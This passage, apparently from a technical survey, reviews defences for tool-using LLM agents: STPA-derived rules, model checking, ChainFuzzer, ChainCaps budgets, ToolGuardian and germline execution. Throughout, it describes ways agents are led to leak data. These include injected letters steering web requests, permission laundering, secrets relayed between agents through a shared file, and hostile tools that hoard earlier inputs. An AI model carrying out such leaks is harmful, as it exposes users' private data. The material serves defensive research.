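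The protection depends on which capabilities the developer makes available. Zhao and colleagues note that the compiler can't stop an attacker from misusing a capability that the task needs. For example, an assistant that may send email can still send the wrong email. In their runs of AgentDojo, 8 attacks succeeded in 1,898 trials.

Placeholders may also nest without end, so the harness has to limit their depth. On AgentDojo, agents completed more tasks with LACUNA than with TACIT in seven of the eight combinations of model and type of task. But on 392 customer-service tasks, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calling. The abstract nevertheless describes the two as on par.

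### Deciding what to forbid

A compiler can enforce a rule about hospital letters only after someone realises the rule is needed. To identify such rules, Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, use a method from safety engineering called System-Theoretic Process Analysis (STPA). Engineers use STPA in aviation and for self-driving cars to look for accidents that arise when components interact, even though none of them is faulty.

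Their example is a calendar agent that resolves scheduling conflicts with three tools: `list_events`, `update_event` and `send_email`. A user's new appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease clashes with her meeting with Bob. The agent suggests moving the meeting to the afternoon, and she agrees. The agent then emails her colleagues about the change and mentions the appointment. No attacker is involved in this disclosure.

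The analysis starts with the people the agent might affect and ends with rules that a program can check. Applied to the calendar agent, it runs roughly as follows:

| Step | Privacy | Timely news |
|---|---|---|
| Who is affected? | the user | the other people at the meeting |
| What do they value? | keeping private matters private | hearing about changes promptly |
| What loss could occur? | private information leaks | they hear about a change too late |
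| What could cause it? | an email includes private details | the agent moves a meeting without telling them |
| What must the agent do? | include only essential details, unless the user authorises more | notify everyone promptly |
| What can a program check? | no call to `send_email` contains data that is private to the recipient | one `send_email` to each attendee directly follows every `update_event` |

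The last row contains two kinds of rule. The privacy rule restricts where data may go, so every piece of data needs a label, and anything computed from private data must be at least as private. The notification rule restricts the order of calls and requires some of them. A type check like TACIT's could enforce something close to the privacy rule, but it cannot require the workflow to send an email.

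The same questions would reveal the problem with the mail assistant's deputy. The people affected include the user, the deputy and everyone who has written to the user. An analyst who asks what the user would lose if the deputy saw an answer would recognize that the final answer is a sink that needs a rule. A reviewer looking only for attackers or for requests to outsiders could easily miss that sink.

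Doshi and colleagues then sort the possible flows into those a harness should always block, those it should require, those it can allow without asking, and those that need the user's confirmation. A cautious developer might forbid every email after a call to `list_events`, while a less cautious one might allow emails that follow an approved template. Doshi and colleagues limit the method to agents with a narrow purpose, because it is hard to list what could go wrong with a general-purpose agent.

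### Searching a model of the tools

The rules may be wrong or incomplete. Doshi and colleagues tested theirs with Alloy, a language for describing systems in logic. Their description covers the steps of a run, the tools and the messages between them, and labels each message by how secret and how trusted it is. A condition called `private_leak` is true if private data reaches a tool that isn't authorised to receive it. Alloy's analyser searches every possible run up to a fixed length for one that makes the condition true.

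Without the rules, the analyser quickly found such runs, including one that puts private data in an external email. With the rules and confirmation steps, it found none. It still found harmless runs, such as creating an event, moving it and telling the participants, so the restrictions had not simply blocked everything the agent could do.

Spera's closure check also searches a model of the tool set, but it tracks only which abilities the agent has. The Alloy model includes the order of the calls and the labels on the data, so it can distinguish an agent that reads a private event before sending an email from one that sends the email first.

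A clean result proves that no run of the model up to the chosen length breaks the rules. The limit on length is often reasonable because many failures need only a few steps, such as the mail assistant's leak, which takes two calls. With three tools, there are 88,572 possible sequences of up to ten calls, even without counting differences in the data they carry. But a real agent may make hundreds of calls in a turn, and a search limited to ten calls can't find a leak that first appears at the eleventh.

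The larger problem is whether the model matches the real system. It may go wrong in several ways:

- A tool may do more than its description says. Suppose an analyst models the `write_file` tool described by Adam and colleagues from its description. The model will then leave out the message it sends to a metrics service.
- The analyst may leave out a channel. If the model covers the text in a web address but not the choice of page, it won't include a leak through a list of 64 permitted pages, however long the runs are.
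- A label may be wrong. Doshi and colleagues want servers for the Model Context Protocol to declare what each tool can do, how confidential its data is and how far to trust its output. They accept that clients would need some reason to believe tools from strangers, such as certification.
- The running harness may not enforce the rules. In the model, the checks always happen. Doshi and colleagues had still to build the program that would intercept real tool calls and apply them.

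The analysis therefore shows that the rules would work in a system that matched the description, but a developer still has to check whether the real system matches it.

### Testing the running system

Testing avoids this gap because it uses the actual model, harness and tools. Security testers often use fuzzing, which means running a program on many generated inputs and watching for failures. Random inputs are inefficient for an agent with dozens of tools, because most sequences of calls make no sense and the model may not follow the sequence the tester wants. *ChainFuzzer* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2026) instead works backwards from dangerous operations.

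The program first reads the tools' source code and looks for calls to particular library functions, such as those that run a command or request a web address. A tool counts as a sink only if its input can affect what the function receives. `get_page` would count because its argument becomes the address, but a tool that always contacts the same address would not.

ChainFuzzer traces possible chains of tools from each sink back to a source. One tool can feed another directly, as when a search returns a web address and a download tool accepts one, or indirectly, by saving a file that a later tool reads. These rules produce many chains that no sensible task would use, so a language model filters them out.

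Next, ChainFuzzer writes a request meant to make the agent follow the chain, runs the agent and compares its calls with the intended chain. If the agent skipped a step or used the wrong file, ChainFuzzer revises that part of the request and tries again. It accepts a request once the agent has followed the chain five times in a row. Finally, it places hostile test data at the start of the chain, either in the user's message or in outside content such as a web page. It records a vulnerability only if monitoring shows that the data reached the sink and met the test for that kind of sink.

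Wu and colleagues applied this to 20 popular open-source agent applications with 998 tools, running the agents on GPT-5.1. They found 199 sink tools and 2,388 candidate chains, and obtained reliable requests for 2,213 of the chains. They confirmed 365 distinct vulnerabilities in 19 of the 20 applications. Of the vulnerabilities, 302 needed more than one tool and 63 needed only one. When they turned off the search for chains, they found only 63, so a tester who examined tools one at a time would probably have missed most of the problems.

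| Operation at the end of the chain | Hostile data from the user | Hostile data from outside content | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| running a system command | 82 | 39 | 121 |
| running program code | 53 | 26 | 79 |
| making a network request | 44 | 53 | 97 |
| sending a database statement | 29 | 16 | 45 |
| filling in a text template | 17 | 6 | 23 |
| **all** | **225** | **140** | **365** |

In 200 of the 365 cases (55%), the chain ends by running a command or code. The table doesn't separate single-tool from multi-tool cases, but since only 63 cases involve a single tool, at least 137 of the 302 multi-tool cases end this way. The table has no category for writing a file, which usually matters here as a middle step, as when an agent downloads a supposed software fix, saves it and runs it. The database statements may read or write.

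Whether all 365 are flaws depends on who uses the application. In 225 cases, the hostile data came from the user. These cases are serious if a company runs the agent on its own servers for the public, but much less serious if the user runs it on her own computer, where she could type the same command herself. The 140 cases that start with outside content are a problem in either setting.

The 97 network requests are the most relevant to read-only tools, but they don't quite match the mail assistant's leak. ChainFuzzer checks whether hostile data can direct a request to an internal address, such as a machine behind a company's firewall. It doesn't check whether a request to a public website contains private data, so the mail assistant could pass and still send a bank balance to a stranger.

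### Why a clean test is not a proof

When ChainFuzzer confirms a vulnerability, it saves the request and the calls that followed, so a developer can repeat the failure without trusting anyone's labels or formal model. One such failure is enough to show that a workflow is unsafe, but a workflow may still be unsafe however many test runs succeed.

Part of the reason is that a tester can try only some of the possible inputs. The mailbox could contain any letter, and the leak may happen only with one that nobody thought of. ChainFuzzer also never obtained reliable requests for 175 of its candidate chains, so those remain untested. Wu and colleagues checked 200 of the chains by hand and found 183 entirely correct. Most of the chains ChainFuzzer finds are therefore real, but this check doesn't measure how many real chains it misses. The one application without a confirmed vulnerability may have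 flaws outside the five categories, or flaws that didn't appear in the test environment.

The model's randomness also makes leaks harder to find by testing. If a particular letter causes a leak in one run out of 100, there is a 60% chance that 50 runs with that letter will all be clean. To rule out a leak rate of 1% or more with 95% confidence, a tester needs 299 clean runs. That result covers only the letter and system tested. An attacker can write a different letter. If the developer switches to a new language model, the agent may make different calls from the same letter, even if the tools' code hasn't changed.

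## Can the rules be enforced while the workflow runs?

The model can reach a website only through a `get_page` call that the harness runs, no matter what an attacker writes in a letter. Code in or next to the harness can therefore check each call when the model requests it and refuse any that break a rule.

The rules often have to be checked while the workflow runs because the model chooses how to combine the tools as it goes. A check made at the start has to rely on worst-case assumptions about which tools the model will call, in what order and with what data.

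*Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (Schneider, Faujdar and colleagues, 2026) measures how much such a rule forbids. In this system, each tool's policy records the sensitivity of the data it handles (public, internal, confidential or restricted), whether that data may leave the organisation, and the network zones where the tool may run. When a session starts, the system gives the whole set of tools the highest sensitivity found in any policy, keeps every ban on sending data out, and allows only the zones that all the policies share. It rejects any set that combines confidential data with a tool that reaches outside the organisation. If mail counts as confidential, the system rejects `search_mail` together with `get_page` before the user has asked for anything, even if she only wants to look up a museum's opening hours.

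Checking all the tools together also reveals conflicts that checking them in pairs would miss. Suppose one tool may run in zones A and B, another in B and C, and a third in A and C. Every pair shares a zone, but there is no zone where all three may run.

Schneider and colleagues tried this on 32 tools governed by 16 policies. The default mode also requires every tool to be cleared for the most sensitive data in the set. It rejected 79.2% of the 120 pairs of policies and 95.5% of the 560 triples. A looser mode lets a tool without that clearance process sensitive data, as long as the output keeps its classification. This mode rejected 42.5% of the pairs and 60.5% of the triples. These percentages describe one catalogue, not the tasks users want done, but an agent that can't combine most triples of policies won't be much use. The system therefore has a second phase, which records the sensitivity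 of the data the agent actually touches and ends the session before a call that would break a policy.

### Labels on tool results

An enforcer needs a record of where each piece of data in a call came from in order to judge it. FIDES, which Microsoft researchers presented in 2025, labels the agent's state and its tools' inputs and outputs for confidentiality and integrity. A confidentiality label records who may see a value, and an integrity label records whether an untrusted party may have influenced it. CaMeL, published the same year by Debenedetti and colleagues, has a model write a program before any model reads untrusted data, and labels the values in that program.

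*Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues, 2026) reports that both systems label a tool's reply mainly by which tool produced it and what went into the call, and that CaMeL also considers the type of content. When a program requests a call, ordinary code checks the labels on the data and refuses the call if the recipient isn't cleared to see it. A policy that keeps private mail away from websites therefore blocks the hotel program's call to `get_page`, as noninterference does.

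The drop in completed tasks under enforcement varies widely. On AgentDojo, CaMeL completed most of the office tasks with one model but almost none of the travel tasks with another, though those results combine the effect of labels with the effect of committing to a program in advance. Garby and colleagues came closer to isolating the effect of labels. Their agent, Randori, completed about a sixth fewer banking tasks when they forbade endorsement.

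### A budget for each value

*ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) gives every value a budget, the set of sinks it may still reach, because a label such as "secret" doesn't record where a value may go. For example, a company may allow a salary figure to appear on a manager's screen or go to one internal address, but nowhere else.

ChainCaps is designed to prevent what its creators call **permission laundering**. In their example, an agent reads a salary spreadsheet, fetches industry figures from the web, summarises the two together and emails the summary to a distribution list. Each tool's permissions allow its own call, but the email contains salaries that should have stayed inside the company. The summary doesn't show that part of it came from a restricted file.

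ChainCaps is a proxy that sits between the agent and its tool servers and intercepts every tool call and result. It requires no changes to the model or the tools, but each tool needs a manifest that declares what the tool reads, where it can send data and what it may pass on.

A sink is written as an operation with a scope, for example a web request to any address that begins with `https://www.hotel.example/`. A budget that contains a sink also contains every narrower version of it. The proxy applies these rules:

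1. **Sources.** A value *v* that enters from a source *o*, such as the mailbox, starts with the budget that the manifest gives that source: *B*(*v*) = Init(*o*).
2. **Transfers.** If tool *t* computes *y* from the values *x*₁, …, *x*ₖ, then *B*(*y*) = Pass(*t*) ∩ *B*(*x*₁) ∩ … ∩ *B*(*x*ₖ). Pass(*t*) is the tool's own limit on where its output may go.
3. **Sinks.** A call to *t* with arguments *a* needs a particular sink, written Req(*t*, *a*). The proxy allows the call only if that sink is in the budget of every value that contributed to *a*.

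The proxy can't determine which words in the model's context led it to write a particular argument, so it assigns the context a budget equal to the intersection of the budgets of everything that has entered it. Whatever the model writes inherits that budget.

Jiang and colleagues support the design with a counting argument. With *m* sinks there are 2<sup>*m*</sup> possible sets of sinks, so a system with one label per set needs 2<sup>*m*</sup> labels, whereas a budget needs only *m* bits. The advantage is convenience, since *m* bits also have 2<sup>*m*</sup> possible values. They accept that richer label systems can express the same policies, and the LLMbda calculus already uses sets as labels.

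### The mail assistant under ChainCaps

Suppose the developer allows letters to reach only the user's screen, and everything else to reach the screen or any website. The budgets are then {screen} and {screen, web}. None of the three tools adds a limit, so Pass(*t*) is {screen, web} for each.

| Step | Budget of the new text | Budget of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| the user asks about the hotel's check-in time | {screen, web} | {screen, web} |
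| `search_mail` returns the booking confirmation | {screen} | {screen} |
| `summarise` shortens the confirmation | {screen} | {screen} |
| the model writes the hotel's address as an argument for `get_page` | {screen} | {screen} |

The last call needs web access, which the address's budget doesn't include, so the proxy blocks it. It would also block a request to the stranger's website, no matter how the model had rewritten the bank balance.

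The hotel task therefore fails, as it did with the type check in TACIT. If the user then asks for a museum's opening hours, the proxy refuses that too, even if she typed the museum's address herself, because the context still contains a letter. ChainCaps can reset the context's budget between tasks, which reduced wrongful refusals from 45% to 20% in a set of hard but harmless scenarios. The reset is safe only if the harness also empties the context, because otherwise the model could copy an old letter into a new request.

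The developer could instead widen the mailbox's budget to include addresses under `https://www.hotel.example/`. The hotel request would then work, and requests to the stranger's website would still be blocked. But the model could also send the hotel the user's bank balance, because a budget limits who receives the data, not which part of it they receive.

### The non-amplification theorem

The central guarantee of ChainCaps concerns calls that go ahead without a special release. If the proxy allows such a call to *t* with arguments *a*, then

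Req(*t*, *a*) ∈ Init(*o*) for every source *o* that contributed to *a*

In the mail assistant, an address sent to a website can depend on a letter only if the developer allowed letters to reach that website from the start. No sequence of searches, summaries and rewrites can add to the destinations the developer allowed.

The proof is by induction over the steps that produced the arguments. A value taken directly from its source has the budget Init(*o*). Every later step intersects budgets, so an output's budget is a subset of each input's budget, and so of the initial budget of each source behind it. Tracking the context can only remove more sinks. The proxy allows a call only if the sink the call needs is in the budgets of all the contributing values, so that sink must also be in the initial budget of every source behind them.

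This is consistent with Spera's result that two safe sets of tools can be unsafe when combined. The assistant still has both abilities, reading mail and contacting websites, but ChainCaps limits the data that passes from one to the other.

The theorem depends on correct initial budgets and on a complete record of which sources contributed to each call. The tool's own limit, Pass(*t*), matters when that record is incomplete. If a tool uses only its recorded inputs, a permissive Pass(*t*) does no harm, because the intersection still applies. If the tool also reads a file that the manifest omits, Pass(*t*) is the only limit on where that file's contents may go.

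### How ChainCaps performed

Jiang and colleagues tested the proxy with real tool calls on 82 tasks, 56 with attacks and 26 of ordinary work. They ran every task three times with each of five models, with and without ChainCaps. An attack counted as successful if restricted data reached a sink outside its budget, or was used to authorise one.

| Model | Attack success without ChainCaps | Attack success with it | Ordinary tasks completed with it |
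|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 67.8% | 4.8% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 25.2% | 3.6% | 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 31.5% | 3.6% | 96% |
| GPT-5.1 | 53.6% | 2.4% | 100% |
| Qwen 3.5 | 53.0% | 0.0% | 96% |

Without ChainCaps, all five models completed every ordinary task. The proxy added a median of 0.13 milliseconds per call.

The size of the drop is weak evidence of how much the proxy would help in ordinary use, because Jiang and colleagues wrote the tasks themselves and concentrated on failures of composition, the problem their proxy addresses. They also defined success by the same budgets that the proxy enforces, so a leak to a permitted recipient wouldn't count. In a somewhat more independent test, they replayed 46 attacks adapted from two other groups' benchmarks, and the proxy blocked all of them.

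The comparison with rival systems is weaker evidence. Jiang and colleagues applied their own simplified models of FIDES and PFI (a system that isolates tool calls from one another) to recorded runs, instead of running the complete systems. On the GPT-5.1 runs, ChainCaps blocked 59.5%, the model of FIDES 16.1% and the model of PFI 10.1%. These results show that a single secrecy label distinguishes fewer cases than a set of sinks, but not how the complete systems would have performed.

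The quality of the manifests had a large effect:

| Manifests | Attacks blocked | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| written by experts | 100% | 100% |
| written with a checklist | 90.9% | 100% |
| naive | 27.3% | 50% |

The naive manifests did badly in both columns, so their mistakes did more than make the system more permissive. The percentages in the middle column match 11, 10 and 3 blocked attacks out of 11, which suggests the test was small. Still, the result is a serious problem for wider use, because many servers omit even the Model Context Protocol's four yes-or-no hints, and a manifest requires much more information.

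### Rules about the order of calls

An enforcer can also check the order of the calls, without tracking individual values. *ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) checks each tool before admitting it, then checks its calls during the run. It uses rules written in a logic language, so the same facts always lead to the same decision, and a reviewer can see which rule produced it.

In their main example, an agent has a database tool and a client for managing projects on GitHub. The admission check rejects a tool if it both reads sensitive data and communicates with outsiders. The database tool only reads records, and the GitHub client only contacts outsiders, so both pass. During the run, the task permits database reads and project updates, so each call also passes on its own. But another rule covers the pair:

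sensitive read at step *i*, external update at step *j*, *i* before *j*, and no exception ⇒ refuse

The agent reads the database first and then tries to update the project, so ToolGuardian refuses the workflow.

The rule doesn't check whether any record went into the update, so it would also refuse an agent that reads a customer's record and then marks an unrelated job as finished, unless someone had written an exception. ChainCaps's context budget is similarly coarse, because it treats everything the model writes after reading a letter as if it came from that letter.

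Ravindran and Deochake tested 20 scenarios, 12 with a single call and 8 with several. The logic rules decided all 20 correctly, as did a version in ordinary code and one that used a language model. Since Ravindran and Deochake designed the scenarios together with the rules, this mainly shows that the rules work as intended. Their tests with some rules removed are more informative. Without its rules about combinations, the ordinary code still decided all 12 single-call scenarios correctly, but only 4 of the 8 with several calls.

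The admission check was strict even with harmless tools. With the fullest evidence, including source code, the logic rules rejected two of eight harmless tools and admitted the other six only with restrictions. They rejected seven of eight malicious tools and restricted the last.

### Labels that follow files between agents

An enforcer that watches each agent separately can lose track of data when the agents share files. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues, 2026) gives an example with two coding agents. Agent A reads a secret and writes an encoded version of it to `notes.txt`. Agent B reads `notes.txt` and posts the text to an approved website. The secret reaches the website even though A never uses the network and B never opens the file the secret came from.

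Hegelich and colleagues keep a ledger with a label for every file and every agent. Write ℓ for a label and ⊔ for the operation that combines two labels by keeping the more restrictive part of each. The ledger changes as follows:

when A writes a file: ℓ(file) ← ℓ(file) ⊔ ℓ(A)

when B reads it: ℓ(B) ← ℓ(B) ⊔ ℓ(file)

After A reads the secret, A's label includes "sensitive". The file gets that label when A writes it, and B gets the label when B reads the file. The harness then blocks B's request to the website. It blocks the request even if A encodes the secret, because the ledger doesn't inspect the text.

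Each label has separate parts for trust and secrecy. Reading a stranger's bug report lowers an agent's trust level but doesn't make its data secret. Once the agent has turned the report into a structured summary, the harness lets it edit files and run isolated tests, but not use the network or run arbitrary commands. Cleaning up suspicious text can raise its trust level, but sensitive data can become public only if the secret is removed or the data is explicitly released.

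Hegelich and colleagues compared this with simpler rules on 12 attacks and 12 ordinary programming workflows, each with five steps.

| Rule | Attacks blocked | Ordinary workflows blocked |
|---|---|---|
| check each call by itself | 8 of 12 | 0 of 12 |
| after any untrusted or sensitive input, block all calls with side effects | 12 of 12 | 10 of 12 |
| two-part labels that follow files | 12 of 12 | 0 of 12 |

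The middle row shows that a single mark can quickly stop a workflow. Ten of the workflows began with outside text, such as a bug report or a crash log, and stopped as soon as the agent tried to edit code or run a test.

The last row is less certain. The team wrote the workflows itself and tested them with prepared calls instead of a live agent. In a larger set of single calls, the harness at first blocked 124 of 132 attacks, and blocked all 132 only after the team added rules for the gaps. The design also treats a summary of a stranger's report as more trustworthy than the report, although the stranger can influence a written summary far more than a choice from a short list of categories.

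### Tools whose code is hostile

These systems monitor what enters and leaves a tool. They generally label the output as if it depended only on the inputs of the current call. That is true of a pure function, but a tool that someone has merely described as harmless may store data from earlier calls and use it in later outputs.

Suppose the user installed `summarise` from a stranger, and it secretly stores the letters it receives. In a later session, the model gives it a public web page, and `summarise` returns a summary with part of an old letter hidden in it. Because the web page is public, the enforcer labels the summary public and lets `get_page` send it to any website.

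Aun and colleagues found this gap in CaMeL's published interpreter. A tool received the body of a private email in one call and returned it in a later call. CaMeL labelled the returned text public and allowed the program to email it to an untrusted recipient, though it blocked the program from sending the same text directly. The attack worked in both normal and strict mode, but only if the developer had listed the tool as side-effect-free, which CaMeL does not verify. The test shows that the gap exists, but Aun and colleagues wrote the test programs by hand, so it doesn't measure how often programs written by a model would trigger it.

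A digital signature doesn't help, because it proves who published a tool, not what the code does. Restricting where the tool can connect helps only partly. Aun and colleagues tested MCPGuard-Dynamic, a program from Meta that limits the files and destinations a tool can reach. In its stronger configurations, it stopped every attempt to contact an unlisted server. But a malicious text-recognition tool saved personnel and board documents from earlier calls and added them to its next request to the text-recognition service it was allowed to use. The tool leaked the documents this way in all three trials of each of the seven configurations.

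Aun and colleagues call the missing property **invocation purity**, which means that a call sends each destination only data it may see. This is weaker than purity because the call may still contact an outside service. A tool can violate invocation purity by carrying over data from an earlier call or by mixing items within a single call, such as by copying a salary sheet into a request that should contain only an invoice.

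Their remedy, **germline execution**, doesn't require anyone to inspect the code:

1. The harness starts the tool in a clean process that never receives user data.
2. For each call, it groups the possible recipients according to what they may see.
3. It makes a fresh copy of the clean process for each group and gives the copy only the data that the group may see.
4. A separate program, the broker, delivers a request to a destination only if it comes from that destination's copy.
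5. The harness destroys the copies after the call.

Hidden code still runs, but the copy that can contact a website holds only data that the website may see. Aun and colleagues prove a form of noninterference with each destination as the observer. The proof covers any tool code, provided that the copies are properly isolated, the starting process contains no user data and the policy labels are correct. It does not cover leaks through timing.

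They also ran 153 attacks against a series of defences, using tools they had written with hidden code.

| Defence | Attack runs with a detected leak |
|---|---|
| signature check | 114 |
| signature check and labels on each call's output | 108 |
| the above, with limits on files and destinations | 51 |
| the above, with a new process for every call | 15 |
| one clean copy per call, holding all the inputs | 9 |
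| germline execution | 0 |

Labels alone prevented few leaks in the test. Clearing the tool's memory between calls prevented most of the remaining leaks, and separating the data by recipient prevented the rest. The test counted a leak only if a planted string reached the wrong recipient in a form the detector could decode, so for other encodings, only the proof supports the claim that leaks are prevented.

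A call that needed one copy took 10 to 49 milliseconds, and each further copy adds time. Tools lose any useful data they keep in memory unless they store it through the broker, which labels it.

The harness can't copy a tool that runs on someone else's server, so it has to treat any reply as possibly containing everything the server was ever allowed to access. In one test, this rule blocked three public posts by an honest remote tool, while ordinary labels blocked one. Germline execution also doesn't stop a tool from sending a harmful command that contains no private data, such as an instruction to delete a file.

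### Who approves the exceptions

Labels and budgets become more restrictive as a session goes on. A budget can only lose sinks, and reading one letter is enough to bar everything the model writes afterwards from being sent to the web. A useful assistant therefore needs some form of declassification.

In ChainCaps, this approval is a signed token that works once, for one request and the data behind it. The user could approve the hotel's web address, and a stranger couldn't reuse that approval for another website. But someone still has to judge the request, and if the address ends in `?ref=44710622`, the user may not be able to tell whether the number is her booking reference or part of her bank details.

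People may also stop reading approval requests when they are frequent. Hegelich and colleagues argue that users learn from opaque warnings to bypass the checks or approve whatever appears. Their harness decodes disguised commands and explains them before asking for approval. But even a careful user sees only one release at a time, so the problem of aggregation remains.

A standing exception, such as allowing letters to reach the hotel's website, needs no further approval but remains open to misuse. It suits a destination the user would trust with anything in her mailbox. A single-use token is better for a stranger's website, if such requests are rare enough for her to examine each one.

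### Who writes the manifests

The manifest is another weak point, particularly if the tool's author writes it. Jiang and colleagues acknowledge that a malicious server can defeat ChainCaps by hiding an effect or declaring too loose a limit on its output. Their proxy checks for common errors, such as a scope that covers every address, but a deliberately false declaration may look valid.

Aun and colleagues reduce this risk by having the organisation that uses the tool decide who may see each item. The tool's author only declares which destinations the tool contacts. A false declaration can change how many copies run, but it can't give a destination access to more data.

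If a tool has no manifest, ChainCaps looks for words in its name and description that suggest a sink, and it refuses calls to sinks it doesn't recognise. This word search found every sink in the collection Jiang and colleagues examined, but with many false alarms. Someone writing a hostile tool could also word its description to avoid detection.

### Flows the enforcer cannot see

Most of the attacks that still succeeded against ChainCaps passed data through a channel it could not monitor. An agent can write a script that runs later, or use a shell command that passes data from one program to another. The proxy can check the request to write the script or run the command, but not what the programs do afterwards.

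The mail assistant has similar gaps even without a shell. A proxy in front of the tool servers doesn't check the letters that the harness sends to a remote model. It also doesn't check the final answer, which may go to the deputy or to a chat window that loads images. The developer has to add checks at those points, or send answers through a tool that the proxy can inspect.

Moving enforcement into the operating system makes scripts and network connections visible but loses information about the data. MCPGuard-Dynamic could detect that the text-recognition tool was contacting a permitted service, but not that the request contained a document from an earlier call. Aun and colleagues suggest running each germline copy under such restrictions, so that one layer limits where the code can connect and the other limits what data it has. They have not measured how well the combination works.
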